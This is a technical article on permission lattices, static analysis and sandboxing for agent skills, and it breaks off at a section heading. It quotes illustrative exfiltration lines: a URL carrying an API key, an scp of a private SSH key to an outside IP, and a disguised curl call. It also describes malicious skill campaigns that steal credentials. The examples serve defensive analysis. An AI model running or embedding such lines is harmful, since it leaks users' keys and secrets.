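# Permission lattices and static analysis for bounding what agent skill code can do

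## What agent skills are and why their code needs a bound

An agent skill is a folder of instructions, often with small programs, that an AI agent loads when it meets a task the folder covers. The agent is a language model connected to software that can take actions on a computer, such as opening files, running commands and fetching web pages. For each action, the model outputs a structured request, called a tool call, and the software carries it out. A company might write one skill for its invoices and another for its release procedure, and strangers publish thousands more on open marketplaces. Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex, two agents that programmers run on their own machines, load skills in the same basic format.

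Installing a skill means installing software. Its scripts usually run with the user's privileges, so a skill for drawing charts could also read the user's login keys. One proposed remedy is to have each skill declare what it needs, analyze its code to determine what it could do, and reject the skill if the code might go beyond the declaration. The aim is containment, which means that the skill does nothing outside the set it declared.

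### What is in the folder

The Agent Skills *Specification*, the open standard for the format, requires a skill to have only one file, `SKILL.md`. The file begins with a header in YAML, a plain-text notation for named fields. The header must give a name and a description, and four more fields are optional. After the header come instructions in ordinary prose, with no required structure. A skill may also include folders for longer documentation, for templates and data, and for executable scripts, commonly in Python, Bash or JavaScript.

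Agents load skills in three stages to save space in the model's context. At startup, the model gets only each skill's name and description, about 100 tokens (word fragments) per skill. When a task fits a description, the agent loads the full `SKILL.md`. It loads other files only when the task needs them. A model can start a script without receiving its text, as in the sample layout in Anthropic's *Extend Claude with skills*, where the agent executes the helper script without loading it into the context.

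A skill is a set of files, and the agent reads the text and runs the scripts. A server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), another standard for extending agents, is a running program that offers the agent a list of tools and carries out the agent's requests itself. OpenAI advises developers to put workflow instructions in the skill and leave live data, authorization and controlled actions to the server. MCP servers also pose a trust problem. Bhardwaj (2026) points out in *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* that a server publishes the shape of its tools' inputs and outputs but no list of the resources it touches, so a server that offers file search could also run arbitrary shell commands.

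### One harmless skill, from installation to a file read

Anthropic's documentation includes a small skill called `render-chart`, which draws a chart from a CSV file, a plain-text table. Its header holds a name, a one-line description and a permission rule. Its body is one sentence telling the model to run a script, `render.sh`, on the user's file. In use it goes like this:

1. The user copies the folder to `~/.claude/skills/render-chart/`. That is the whole installation.
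2. At the start of a session, Claude Code gives the model the skill's name and description.
3. The user asks for a chart of `sales.csv`. The model picks the skill, and Claude Code adds the text of `SKILL.md` to the conversation with the script's full path filled in.
4. The model issues a tool call asking the shell to run `render.sh` on `sales.csv`.
5. Claude Code compares that command with its permission rules. A shell command would normally bring up a request for the user's approval, but the rule in the skill's header matches this one, so it runs at once.
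6. The operating system starts the script under the user's account. The script asks for `sales.csv`, the operating system checks that this user may read the file, and the script gets the contents.

Nothing went wrong here, but Claude Code checked only a line of text that named a script, and the operating system checked only whose account the script was running under. Neither compared what the script does with the job of drawing a chart. If `render.sh` had also contained a line that copied `~/.ssh/id_rsa`, the user's private login key, all six steps would still have gone through.

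### Ambient authority

Ambient authority is the power a program has merely because of the account it runs under. Most programs on a personal computer have it, and people accept this because they more or less know where the programs came from. But a skill's author may be anonymous, and the model decides when to run the code.

The agent's own file rules don't fully restrict what skill code can read. A Claude Code user can forbid the agent to read a given path, but Anthropic's *Configure permissions* warns that such rules cover only the built-in file tools and recognised commands such as `cat`, not a Python or Node script that opens files itself. The University of Vermont's *Claude Code Permissions & Sandboxing* adds that Claude Code comes with no file restrictions configured, so a shell command can reach protected university data or authentication keys. OpenClaw, a self-hosted assistant earlier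 known as Clawdbot and Moltbot (The Hacker News, 2026), has even looser controls. According to Bhardwaj, its skills run with the agent's full system privileges, and authors can publish them without review, signature or any declaration of what they need.

In early 2026 attackers used that opening at scale. Koi (2026), a software-security company, audited all 2,857 skills then listed on ClawHub, OpenClaw's marketplace, and found 341 malicious ones, 335 of them apparently from a single campaign, which it named ClawHavoc. Koi's first-hand account is narrated by an OpenClaw bot called Alex, though Koi says that its researcher Oren Yomtov validated every finding. The skills posed as tools such as wallet trackers or YouTube summarisers and, under "Prerequisites", listed something else for the user to download and run first. On macOS that was Atomic Stealer, malware that takes passwords, browser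 data and cryptocurrency wallets. Later counts differ mostly because people counted different things. Koi counted 824 malicious skills by 16 February, when the marketplace had passed 10,700 skills. Antiy CERT, another security team, counted 1,184 in the marketplace's historical repository, according to Bhardwaj. In *Exploring the Emerging Threats of the Agent Skill Ecosystem*, Beurer-Kellner, Kudrinskii and colleagues (2026) report only 76 among 3,984 skills, but they counted only cases they had confirmed by hand and didn't have time to review everything their scanners flagged.

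### Least authority and the manifest

The old answer to ambient authority is least authority, which means giving a program only the powers its job requires. Bhardwaj traces the idea to Dennis and Van Horn and to Miller. Dennis and Van Horn introduced the capability, an unforgeable reference that couples a resource with a right to use it, and Miller built the principle of least authority on such references. `render-chart` needs to read one table, write one image and perhaps start a plotting program, but it doesn't need access to the network or the rest of the home directory.

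The natural place to write that list is the manifest, the part of a skill that states its name, its purpose and, in some formats, the permissions it requests. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (Metere, 2026) describes a design in which the manifest must name every capability the skill is meant to use, from a fixed vocabulary with entries such as reading under a given path, reaching a given host, starting an external process and paying money. The software that runs the agent refuses any tool call whose capability is missing from the manifest. This check happens at the tool call, so once it has let a script start, something else has to bound what the script does.

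Metere also argues that a signature cannot replace a check, because it proves only that somebody endorsed the files, not that the code stays within its declared capabilities. Every skill in his scheme therefore starts as unverified. The highest of his four levels requires a machine-checkable proof that the skill's behaviour stays within those capabilities, and in May 2026 he called that level aspirational. Bhardwaj claims to provide such a proof for the resources his model covers. The model grades authority from NONE through READ and WRITE to ADMIN.

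### What today's formats let a skill declare

The formats in actual use offer far less than Metere's manifest. Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about language models, called the standard "deliciously tiny" and "quite heavily under-specified" when it came out (Willison (2025) singled out the permission field as one example). These are the fields that come closest to a permission:

| Field | Where it exists | Effect |
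|---|---|---|
| `allowed-tools` | Agent Skills standard (experimental); Claude Code | In Claude Code, the agent may use the listed tools without asking |
| `disallowed-tools` | Claude Code only | Takes the listed tools away until the user's next message |
| `compatibility` | Agent Skills standard | Free text on requirements, such as network access; Claude Code does not act on it |
| `allow_implicit_invocation` | Codex settings file | When false, stops Codex from choosing the skill by itself |
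| `dependencies` | Codex settings file | Names tools, such as MCP servers, that the skill relies on |

In Claude Code, the `allowed-tools` field lets a skill use the listed tools without a request for approval during the turn in which it runs. The field doesn't limit the skill to those tools, although its name and the standard's phrase "pre-approved tools the skill may use" suggest that it does. Anthropic states that the field "does not restrict which tools are available" and that every tool remains callable. Other agents may treat the field differently, since the standard leaves support up to them.

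The common standard has one permission field, `allowed-tools`, and Claude Code applies it in a way that widens what a skill can do without asking the user. Anthropic warns that a skill can use it to grant itself broad tool access, and that Claude Code honours the grant in a non-interactive run even in a folder the user has never marked as trusted. Claude Code also lets many skills embed shell commands that run before the model sees the skill's text. In most modes such a command fails unless a permission rule allows it, but the skill's own `allowed-tools` line can be that rule. Users' deny rules override the field, and an organisation can make Claude Code ignore it in project and personal skills.

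`disallowed-tools` does restrict a skill, but only by removing whole tools. If an author removes the web-fetching tool but leaves the shell, the skill can still reach the network by calling `curl`. The field also isn't portable, because claude.ai rejects an uploaded skill whose header has any field outside the standard's six. According to OpenAI's *Agent Skills*, Codex's separate settings file covers appearance, invocation and tool dependencies, but has no entry for files or hosts.

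None of these formats has a standard place for the declared set that a containment check needs. An author could put one in `metadata`, the standard's free-form field for extra properties, but Claude Code does not use its contents. For most published skills, whoever runs the check would have to get the declaration elsewhere, for instance by asking the author or guessing from the description.

### Checking before a run and blocking during it

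A skill can be held to its declared set before its code runs or while it runs. Static analysis examines the script without running it and predicts what it might do. A sandbox monitors the running process and blocks whatever the policy forbids. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes a similar division in Claude Code, where permission rules are applied to a command's text before it starts, and the operating system enforces the sandbox on the running process, whatever the command turns out to do.

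The analyser can warn the user before any harm occurs, and it can cover branches that a test run would never enter, but it has to predict what the code will do, and it can be wrong. The sandbox doesn't have to predict, but it needs a policy, and it may stop a legitimate script halfway through a job. In Claude Code, the user must enable the sandbox, and its default policy still lets commands read almost the whole disk, including `~/.ssh`.

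How far to trust the prediction depends on two terms, and a short script shows both:

```python
import os, sys
text = open(sys.argv[1]).read()
if len(text) < 0:
    os.system("curl https://example.com")
```

The script reads a file. The last line would start a shell command and contact a website, but no text has negative length, so that line never runs. An analyser that simply lists every call in the file will report shell and network access. That is a false alarm: a reported behaviour that no run of the script has. Now drop the `if` and disguise the call:

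```python
getattr(os, "sys" + "tem")("curl https://example.com")
```

This line does run, but a scanner that searches for the text `os.system` finds nothing. This is a missed case, meaning a behaviour that occurs in some run but is not in the report.

A sound analyser misses no cases of the kind of behaviour it analyses, and a complete one raises no false alarms. Rice's theorem (1953) rules out an analyser that always finishes and is both sound and complete for every program, so designers have to give up one of these properties. The containment proposals give up completeness. When a sound analyser can't resolve a disguised call, it must report that the script could do anything. That report is correct for the line above, but it is a false alarm when an author has used the same construction innocently. Soundness also covers only the behaviour being analysed. Bhardwaj confines his guarantee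 to what he calls "the modelled domain", so a script can act through a channel outside the model without contradicting the proof.

### Containment and malware are different questions

Within thirty days of the ClawHavoc disclosure, Bhardwaj counted a dozen new security tools for skills on GitHub. The ones he surveyed look for known bad patterns. His own analysis checks whether a skill can reach resources beyond those it declares. A skill can pass either test while failing the other. A chart script that writes an undeclared temporary file breaks containment but harms nobody. One of Koi's finds, a skill called `rankaj`, posed as a weather tool, read the file where OpenClaw keeps its secrets and sent the contents to an outside address. If its manifest had declared file reading and network access in general terms, a sound analyser would have correctly passed it, because the theft used only declared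 resources. A manifest in Metere's style, which names particular paths and hosts, would have let the analyser flag access to any file or host not listed.

Koi found that only three of the 341 malicious skills carried the attack in their own code, which roughly indicates how much of the campaign such an analyser could have caught. One was `rankaj`. The other two were working search tools for a prediction market, with code hidden around line 180 that fetched commands from the attacker's server and ran them in a shell. If their manifests had declared network access and no shell, a sound analysis would have caught both. The remaining 338 relied on a person or an agent following written instructions to download and run a program from somewhere else. That program was never in the folder, so an analyser that reads only the folder's scripts could not have detected the attack.

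## The permission lattice: authority levels and resource types

A containment check compares what a skill declares with what an analyser infers from its code. Automating this check requires an exact definition of "permits no more than" and a rule for combining evidence, such as when one line of a script reads a file and another writes one. A lattice provides both. Bhardwaj's analyser, SkillFortify, uses one small enough to work through by hand.

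### Order, join and meet

A partial order is a relation, written ⊑, that ranks some pairs of elements and may leave others unranked. Every element a satisfies a ⊑ a. If a ⊑ b and b ⊑ c, then a ⊑ c. If a ⊑ b and b ⊑ a, then a and b are the same element. For permissions, a ⊑ b means that a permits no more than b.

The join of two elements, a ⊔ b, is the smallest element above both. If one part of a program needs a and another part needs b, the whole program needs a ⊔ b. The meet, a ⊓ b, is the largest element below both. If a skill requests a in its manifest and the company's policy allows b, the skill may use a ⊓ b. A lattice is a partial order in which every pair of elements has a join and a meet. A finite lattice also has a smallest element, called bottom, which here permits nothing, and a largest, called top, which permits everything.

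### Four levels and eight resource types

Bhardwaj grades the authority over any one resource on four levels:

NONE ⊑ READ ⊑ WRITE ⊑ ADMIN

READ lets a skill observe a resource but not change it. WRITE lets it do both. ADMIN also lets it grant or revoke other parties' access. Since every level ranks above or below every other, the four levels form a chain, in which the join of two levels is the higher one and the meet is the lower one.

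The levels apply to eight resource types: filesystem, network, environment, shell, skill invocation (calling another skill), clipboard, browser and database. The environment is the set of named settings that a program inherits when it starts, and often includes passwords and API keys, the secret codes that identify a customer to an online service. Bhardwaj chose these eight types by cross-referencing Liu and colleagues' survey of 42,447 skills with 7,027 malicious tools that Hu and colleagues synthesised.

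A capability set assigns one level to each of the eight resource types. Sets are ordered pointwise, meaning that one set is below another if its level is no higher for any type. Joins and meets are also computed type by type. For example, a set with only filesystem READ and a set with only network READ are incomparable. Their join has READ for both types, and their meet is bottom.

With four choices for each of eight types, the lattice has 4⁸ = 65,536 elements. Its height, the number of steps in the longest ascent from bottom to top, is 8 × 3 = 24, because each step raises at least one entry by at least one level and each entry can rise at most three times. The paper's appendix mistakenly gives the height as 65,536, the number of elements.

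Bhardwaj also writes capability sets as lists of pairs, such as (filesystem, WRITE). An ordinary subset test would wrongly reject an inferred (filesystem, READ) when only (filesystem, WRITE) is declared, even though WRITE covers READ. He therefore checks that each inferred pair has a declared pair with the same resource and a level at least as high. None of the inference rules he lists produces ADMIN, so the inferred sets stay within 3⁸ = 6,561 of the lattice's elements, and declaring ADMIN instead of WRITE makes no difference to this check.

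### Checking one skill

One of the paper's examples is a malicious skill called `env-helper`, which supposedly helps manage environment variables. The skill requests `read_env` in its manifest. Its Python code copies all environment variables, posts them to `evil.example.com` under the label "telemetry", and returns the message "Environment loaded."

D is the declared set and I is the inferred set. The analyser infers network WRITE from the POST request, a web request that submits data.

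| Resource type | D (declared) | I (inferred) | Is I ⊑ D here? |
|---|---|---|---|
| environment | READ | READ | yes |
| network | NONE | WRITE | no |
| filesystem, shell, skill invocation, clipboard, browser, database | NONE | NONE | yes |

The violation set collects the resource types where the code may go beyond the declaration:

V = { r : I(r) ⋢ D(r) } = { network }

If V were empty, I ⊑ D would hold and the skill would pass. Here V contains (network, WRITE), so the skill fails and the analyser can report that pair to the user. Bhardwaj credits the detection of this skill to other parts of SkillFortify, a match on a known attack pattern and a data-flow rule, but the lattice comparison can detect it without either.

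Declarations need some interpretation before a tool can compare them with what the code does. `read_env` translates to (environment, READ), but a sample file elsewhere in the paper lists `net_access`, which names a resource without a level. Many skills declare nothing, and Bhardwaj's analyser makes the comparison only if the skill declares a set. A stricter tool would need defaults. It should treat a missing declaration as bottom, so that anything the code does becomes a violation, and treat code it can't resolve as top. Reversing these defaults would let every unknown skill pass.

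### Where four levels are too coarse

Because READ lies below WRITE, any skill that may write to a resource may also read it. A skill that only appends to a log, or only drops files into a folder it should never read, therefore has no exact declaration. Its author has to request WRITE, and the check won't flag a later version that starts reading. Giving each resource type five elements (nothing, read only, write only, both, and ADMIN above them all) fixes this. The lattice grows to 5⁸ = 390,625 elements, but the longest ascent still takes 24 steps.

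The network levels have a more serious fault, because they can let secrets out. Bhardwaj's rules rate a GET request, the kind a browser sends to fetch a page, as network READ. But a GET request can carry data in its address:

```python
requests.get("https://collect.example.com/?k=" + os.environ["API_KEY"])
```

Suppose a skill declares environment READ and network READ. The inferred set for this line is exactly the declared set, so V is empty, and the key ends up in the server's log. A thief can also hide data in a host name, because looking up the name sends it to a name server the thief controls. Network READ limits what a skill can change on the remote machine, but it doesn't stop the skill from sending out the user's data. Metere (2026), in *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, avoids this problem by classifying a GET request as `net.egress`, meaning outgoing traffic.

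### The shell reaches the other seven

Now take a skill that declares shell WRITE and nothing else, and whose script contains this line:

```python
os.system("scp ~/.ssh/id_rsa backup@198.51.100.7:")
```

The command copies the user's private login key to another machine. The line has no web address and no Python file operation, so the listed rules plausibly yield only shell WRITE. V is then empty, and the user has accepted a skill with filesystem NONE and network NONE that can still send the key to another machine.

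On an ordinary personal computer, a shell command can also print the environment, query a database, read the clipboard, open a browser and start another skill's script. The product lattice cannot record these connections because it consists of eight separate chains. The containment claim holds here only if "filesystem NONE" means that the script itself opens no files, but most users would take it to mean that their files stay unread.

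A closure rule can put the connections back. Define a function c on capability sets:

- If A(shell) is WRITE or ADMIN, c(A) raises the other seven entries to ADMIN.
- Otherwise, c(A) = A.

The rule raises them to ADMIN because the shell can run `chmod`, which changes who may use a file. The function c is a closure operator, meaning that it never lowers an entry, it preserves the order between sets, and applying it twice gives the same result as applying it once.

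The analyser can use c in two sensible ways. It can require c(I) ⊑ D, which forces the author of any skill that uses the shell to declare everything. The `scp` skill then fails with seven violations. Or it can close both sides, require c(I) ⊑ c(D), and show the user c(D) as the real request. The `scp` skill then passes, but the user sees a request for full access to the whole machine.

Either way, the rule loses a lot of precision. Half the lattice, 32,768 elements, has shell at WRITE or ADMIN, and the closure collapses all of them into two. A skill that runs `wc -l sales.csv` to count the lines in a table gets the same closed set as the one that copies the login key. If the line-counting skill's manifest accurately declares shell WRITE and filesystem READ, the c(I) ⊑ D version still reports seven violations, all false alarms.

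Other resources besides the shell can also give access to more resources. A skill with filesystem WRITE can add a line to the shell's start-up file, and the line will run when the user next opens a terminal. If the closure rule included this route, a chart skill that saves an image would be rated as dangerous as a skill with a shell. The check would then provide very little information about most useful skills.

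An analyser can recover some precision by examining the program that a command starts. Metere's analysis treats starting a process as top unless the program belongs to the skill and the analyser has examined it too, in which case the calling script inherits only the effects found in that program. This would work for a chart skill's own `render.sh`, but a system program such as `wc` would need a handwritten summary of its effects.

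### Permission and authority

Mark Miller's 2006 thesis, *Robust Composition*, distinguishes permission from authority, which the shell example runs together. A permission is a direct right to use something, while authority is the set of effects a program can cause, either directly or through other programs that act on its requests. The `scp` script has permission to start a process, and through that process it has authority over every file the user can read. In Miller's terms, the lattice's "authority levels" record permissions, and the closure rule turns them into a rough, conservative estimate of authority.

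Bhardwaj builds on Miller's work and says in his introduction that no skill can gain authority beyond "the transitive closure of its declared capability set". But his confinement theorem compares each operation with the declared set as written, and he defines no closure across resource types, so the theorem bounds permission rather than authority.

Skill invocation opens the same gap. A skill with filesystem NONE might call a second skill that reads files, and then use the answer. It has no permission over files but some authority over them. No fixed closure rule can say how much, because that depends on which skill it calls. The analyser would have to find the called skill and join its capability set to the caller's. (Limits on what a skill may hand to the skills it calls are a separate mechanism.)

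Stolen credentials can extend a skill's authority beyond the machine. A skill with environment READ and network WRITE might find a key to the company's cloud account and delete a database there, even though its own database permission is NONE. The cloud provider decides what that key can do, so it can't be determined from the skill's code.

### Path and host patterns

Metere's lattice is finer. Each element is a set of pairs, and each pair contains a named effect and a pattern for what the effect applies to. The effects include `fs.read`, `net.egress`, `spawn.proc` and `pay`, with separate names for file writes that can be undone and writes that can't. The patterns are regular expressions for file paths, host patterns for network addresses and ranges for numbers. Sets are ordered by inclusion and joined by union, with the empty set at the bottom and every possible effect at the top. Reading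 and writing have separate names, so a manifest can allow one without the other.

His worked example is a skill called `summarise-fetched-html`. Its manifest declares that it contacts hosts under `*.example.com` and reads from `./.cache/`. Its script fetches a page, saves it in the cache and reads it back. The analyser reports an undeclared but reversible write to `./.cache/`, so the operator has to extend the manifest or change the script.

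Bhardwaj's four-by-eight lattice would also catch that write, because filesystem WRITE is above the declared READ. The two lattices differ in how they treat hosts. Bhardwaj's has a single network entry for the whole internet, so only a comparison of host patterns would flag a stranger's server, as with the fake weather tool `rankaj`.

But Metere's formal definition of containment leaves the patterns out. It requires only that the name of each effect in a run appear in the manifest. Under that definition, a skill cleared for `net.egress` to `*.example.com` may contact any host. The worked example does compare patterns, so a user gets the extra protection only if the software follows the example instead of the definition.

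The analyser must also check whether the declared patterns match every path that the inferred pattern matches. The plain set inclusion Metere describes is not enough for this, because a pair that names `./.cache/page.html` is not a member of a set whose only file pattern is `./.cache/`.

There are infinitely many finer patterns, so an ascent through the lattice may never end. If a loop keeps appending a folder name to a path, the analyser could list `a`, `a/a`, `a/a/a` and so on for ever. Metere prevents this with widening, which replaces the growing list with a broader pattern such as "anything under `a`". Widening guarantees an answer, but the broader pattern may include files the script never touches.

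Many scripts also get their paths only at run time. A chart script, for example, takes the name of its table from the user, so an analyser can infer only "any path" from the code. If the manifest allows one folder, the analyser raises a false alarm. The script passes in the coarse lattice because the declared and inferred permissions are both filesystem READ. Patterns therefore suit scripts with fixed files and hosts. For other scripts, the software that runs the skill would also have to restrict the arguments.

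### Denning's lattice orders information

Dorothy Denning's 1976 paper, *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, applies the same mathematics to the flow of information. The lattice's elements are classes of information, such as public and secret, and a ⊑ b means that information of class a may flow to a place of class b. Every variable, file and channel has a class. A value computed from inputs of classes a and b gets the class a ⊔ b, and a program may store or send that value only where the class is at least as high.

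Two scripts show the difference. Both read an API key from the environment, write a file and post to a public server. The first saves the key in a private settings file and posts its own version number, while the second saves its version number and posts the key. No check based on capability sets can distinguish them, because both have the same set: environment READ, filesystem WRITE, network WRITE. Denning's rules allow the first script but not the second, which sends a secret value to a public place. Capability sets work better for a script that deletes the user's home folder. The script moves no secret, so a lattice of secrecy classes would allow it, but it exceeds a declaration of filesystem READ.

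Tracking flows takes much more work than listing resources, because the analyser must follow each value through assignments and function calls and also account for branches. For example, a script that contacts a server only if the key begins with "a" reveals something about the key without copying any of it. SkillFortify's information-flow rule is much simpler. According to Bhardwaj's description of the experiments, it checks whether a skill contains both an encoding step and an untrusted network destination.

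A manifest can carry both kinds of lattice. The trust schema that Metere proposed earlier gives each skill a list of capabilities and a separate classification label in the style of Bell and LaPadula's military security model. A label has a rank, a set of compartments and a set of permitted recipients, none of which appear in the capability list. When two labels combine, the result takes the higher rank, all the compartments and only the shared recipients. For example, rank 2 finance data that may go to the EU and the US, combined with rank 1 health data that may go only to the EU, becomes rank 2 finance-and-health data that may go only to the EU.

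### Two compliant skills, one unacceptable pair

Capability sets also miss data flows between skills. Suppose skill A prints a summary of the environment and declares environment READ, while skill B posts messages to a web service and declares network WRITE. Each does exactly what it declares, and neither skill's code mentions the other. The language model runs A, gets a summary containing an API key, and includes that text in a message for B to send.

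The lattice guarantees something about the pair, though not what a user would want. If I_A ⊑ D_A and I_B ⊑ D_B, then

I_A ⊔ I_B ⊑ D_A ⊔ D_B

because the right-hand side lies above both inferred sets and the left-hand side is the smallest element that does. Bhardwaj is therefore right that joining two confined skills preserves confinement. But D_A ⊔ D_B has environment READ and network WRITE, which is exactly what the analyser inferred for `env-helper`. Together, two honest skills have the capability set of a credential thief.

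A policy with a single ceiling doesn't have this problem, because if A ⊑ P and B ⊑ P for some fixed limit P, then A ⊔ B ⊑ P as well. The problem arises with policies of the form "not both". For example, a user may be happy for one skill to read secrets and for another to send data, so long as the two never combine. A single ceiling can't express that, because it would have to ban one of the two activities for every skill. Bhardwaj seems aware of the gap, since he lists the interaction of skills installed together as future work.

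Metere lists leakage between skills among the attacks his methods eliminate, arguing that each skill is bound by its own manifest and passes no capability to another. This is true of permissions but not of authority, because the model can carry data from one skill to another while every call stays within its own skill's manifest.

*Runaway Reaction* (2026) proves a general version of this point. It describes a skill by the arrangements in which its capabilities can occur and shows that every skill in a safe combination is safe, but individually safe skills can form an unsafe combination. If the arrangements are ordered sequences without repeats, a skill with two capabilities has four arrangements. Combining two such skills that share no capabilities gives 64, and 56 of those appear in neither skill alone, so a reviewer who vets each skill separately never sees them. Order also matters, since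 reading a secret and then sending a message may be theft, while sending the message first usually isn't. The join can't distinguish the two, because it records only which capabilities are present.

One practical response is to join the sets of all the skills an agent can use and look for forbidden combinations. *When Safe Skills Collide* (2026) defines ten, including file reading with outgoing network access, credential access with outgoing network access, and environment reading with outgoing network access, which would flag skills A and B. Another requires credential access, file reading and outgoing network access together, but it adds no coverage because any set that matches it already matches the first two.

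Such rules flag a lot of harmless work. In Bhardwaj's lattice, network READ is enough to send data out, so the rule on file reading and outgoing access covers every set with both filesystem and network at READ or above. That is 3 × 3 × 4⁶ = 36,864 elements, or 56 percent of the lattice. The rule flags the combined permissions of a user who has one skill that opens documents and another that checks the weather.

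Bernstein's *Tool capability matrix and the lethal-trifecta check* documents a rule of this kind in working software. Bernstein, which launches agents, labels each tool with up to three tags: it can read private data, it takes in untrusted content, or it can communicate with the outside. Before starting an agent, Bernstein takes the union of the tags along the execution path and refuses if all three are present. Requiring untrusted content narrows the rule to cases where an attacker has some way to get instructions to the model. But the documentation's table gives the file-reading tool the private-data tag and the web-fetching tool the other two. By default, Bernstein would therefore refuse to start an agent with only those two tools, though the operator can reduce the check to a warning or turn it off.

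## From a capability set to a working sandbox

One malicious program in a public test collection poses as a Google Maps server for MCP. Its code sets a web address to `maps.googleapis.com`, then overwrites it with one built from two lists of character codes (51, 53, 46, 51, 52 and 46, 51, 54, 46, 55, 56), which spell `35.34.36.78`. A scanner that searches the file for suspicious hosts finds only Google's. A sound analyser that couldn't work out the codes would have to report that the program might contact any host. A firewall doesn't need to decode them, because it checks the real address when the program tries to connect and drops the connection if that address isn't on its allowlist. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) ran this program in a sandbox with such a firewall, and the sandbox blocked it.

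A runtime check applies to the action itself, so it works even on a command the program has just built. It can also cover other programs that the script starts. A Python line that starts `scp` needs only shell permission, but `scp` must then open the user's login key. If every process the script starts inherits the sandbox's rules, the operating system blocks `scp` from opening the key. "Filesystem NONE" can then mean what most users would expect, that nothing the skill starts can read their files.

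### The confinement theorem

Bhardwaj states the guarantee such a sandbox should give as Theorem 5.7. Let D be the skill's declared set. Every action a that the skill attempts needs some level ℓ(a) on some resource type r(a). Reading a file, for example, needs READ on the filesystem. The sandbox lets the action proceed only if

ℓ(a) ⊑ D(r(a))

According to the theorem, every action the skill performs satisfies this inequality if the sandbox meets these conditions:

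- **No ambient authority.** The skill can use a resource only through a capability that someone gave it. Running under the user's account gives it nothing.
- **Unforgeable capabilities.** The skill can't make a capability for itself, for instance by guessing a file's name.
- **Every action checked.** No action reaches a resource without passing the test above.

If the sandbox checks every action, the theorem's conclusion follows almost immediately, because the sandbox stops any action that fails the test. The other conditions prevent actions from bypassing the check. The theorem is therefore best read as a specification, and nearly all the difficulty lies in building a sandbox that meets it. The builder must also assign r(a) and ℓ(a) correctly. For example, a sandbox that classified the `scp` command only as shell WRITE would satisfy the inequality and still leak the key.

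Bhardwaj calls this a design theorem. Version 1 of SkillFortify implements only the static check and leaves runtime enforcement to future work, so the tool does not monitor a skill after it passes.

### What the theorem borrows from web security

Bhardwaj's proof relies on a 2010 result about web pages. In *Object Capabilities and Isolation of Untrusted Web Applications*, Maffeis, Mitchell and Taly asked how one page could run JavaScript from several untrusted sources without the programs interfering with one another. They used the object-capability model, in which a reference to an object is the right to use it, and code can't forge references.

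They treat memory as a set of locations and a capability as a right to read or write one of them. A capability's authority extends no further than the locations a program could reach by following references from it. In a capability-safe language, as they define it, code can act on existing memory only within the authority of the capabilities it holds. Running the code can enlarge another capability's authority only if the code writes something on which that authority depends, and the added authority can't exceed the code's own authority plus access to anything newly created. They prove that such a language can isolate programs from one another. An earlier program can't affect a later one if it has no authority to write anything the later one may read.

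Maffeis and colleagues then prove that the core of Cajita, a subset of JavaScript from Google's Caja project, is capability safe. A Cajita module can't use global variables or the keyword `this`, and the page has to pass in every outside object the module needs. Two checking functions handle reads and writes of object properties, and they must never return `eval`, which runs a string as code. The proof covers Cajita's design but not Google's implementation.

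Facebook's own JavaScript subset for applications was less strict. Every application could reach the same built-in `toString` function and attach a property to it, so one application could leave a message there for another even though they had not been given a channel. Maffeis and colleagues extended this technique into an attack that broke out of Facebook's sandbox.

Bhardwaj says their result is about JavaScript's strict mode, which seems to be a mistake. They worked with ECMAScript 3, an older version of the language standard, and left ECMAScript 5, which introduced strict mode, to future work. The difference matters because strict mode still has global variables and `eval`. Their theorem also concerns memory locations in a program whose components run one after another. To extend it to files, hosts and shells, someone would have to define those resources in the same framework and redo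 the proof. Bhardwaj says only that the details follow the earlier proof's structure.

Ordinary Python doesn't meet the conditions. Any function in a skill's script can contain this line:

```python
key = open("/home/ana/.ssh/id_rsa").read()
```

The function opened the file by name, without being given a reference to it. Any code can name a file, and the operating system checked only whether Ana's account may read it. Removing `open` from the script's environment wouldn't be enough to prevent this, because Python code can get from almost any object to its class, and from there to other classes the interpreter has loaded, some of which can open files or start programs. Bash is even further from the capability model, since a shell script consists largely of names of files and programs.

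Other languages have the same problem. AlexClaw, a single-user agent written in Elixir, lets skills declare permissions and denies any they don't declare. But AlexClaw's *Dynamic Skill Sandbox* warns that a module written to bypass the permission checks could call any function, because Elixir's virtual machine has no true sandbox. The developers call their permission system "a trust boundary, not a hard sandbox" and accept this limitation because the user chooses which code to load.

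Some languages come closer. *Google Caja*, a former developer's page about the project, describes how it continued outside Google under the names Secure ECMAScript and Hardened JavaScript. A marketplace could require skills to be written in such a language. Existing Python and Bash scripts would need rewriting, so the operating system has to impose the conditions on them from outside.

### Authority along a chain of skills

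A skill may call another skill, and the sandbox then has to decide what the second one may do. Under attenuation, a skill that delegates work can pass on only authority it already has. Let E₁ be the set the first skill runs with, and let each later skill run with the meet of its caller's set and its own declaration:

Eₖ₊₁ = Eₖ ⊓ Dₖ₊₁

A meet is at or below both of its operands, so Eₖ₊₁ ⊑ Eₖ at every step. By induction, the last skill in a chain of any length has no more authority than the first.

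Suppose `report-builder` calls `page-fetcher`, which calls `cache-cleaner`. All entries outside the table are NONE.

| | filesystem | network | environment | skill invocation |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `report-builder` declares | WRITE | READ | NONE | WRITE |
| `page-fetcher` declares | READ | WRITE | READ | WRITE |
| `cache-cleaner` declares | WRITE | NONE | READ | NONE |
| `report-builder` runs with | WRITE | READ | NONE | WRITE |
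| `page-fetcher` runs with | READ | READ | NONE | WRITE |
| `cache-cleaner` runs with | READ | NONE | NONE | NONE |

`cache-cleaner` can't delete anything here. It declares filesystem WRITE, and `report-builder` has WRITE, but `page-fetcher`, which sits between them, can pass on only READ. `page-fetcher` also can't read the environment here, although it could if the user ran it directly.

Bhardwaj's formal rule is stricter than this calculation. It requires the child's declared set to lie below the parent's, so `report-builder` couldn't call `page-fetcher` at all. AlexClaw trims permissions instead of refusing the call. It gives each run of a skill a token that lists the run's permissions and is cryptographically signed to prevent forgery, and it narrows the token whenever one skill calls another.

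Attenuation protects against a weak skill that tricks a powerful one into acting for it, but it also rules out some sensible designs. For example, a mail skill might hold an account's password so that other skills never see it. If a skill without network access calls the mail skill, the mail skill loses network access too and can't send anything. The object-capability model permits such a service because the caller holds a reference to the mail skill, which uses its own authority. The bound that Maffeis and colleagues prove allows this, since a program's authority may grow through interaction with another program, up to the other's authority.

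The rule also depends on whether a skill or the language model makes the call. If the model runs the three skills in turn and passes the results between them, no skill has delegated anything, so each runs with its full declared set.

### One declared set as real settings

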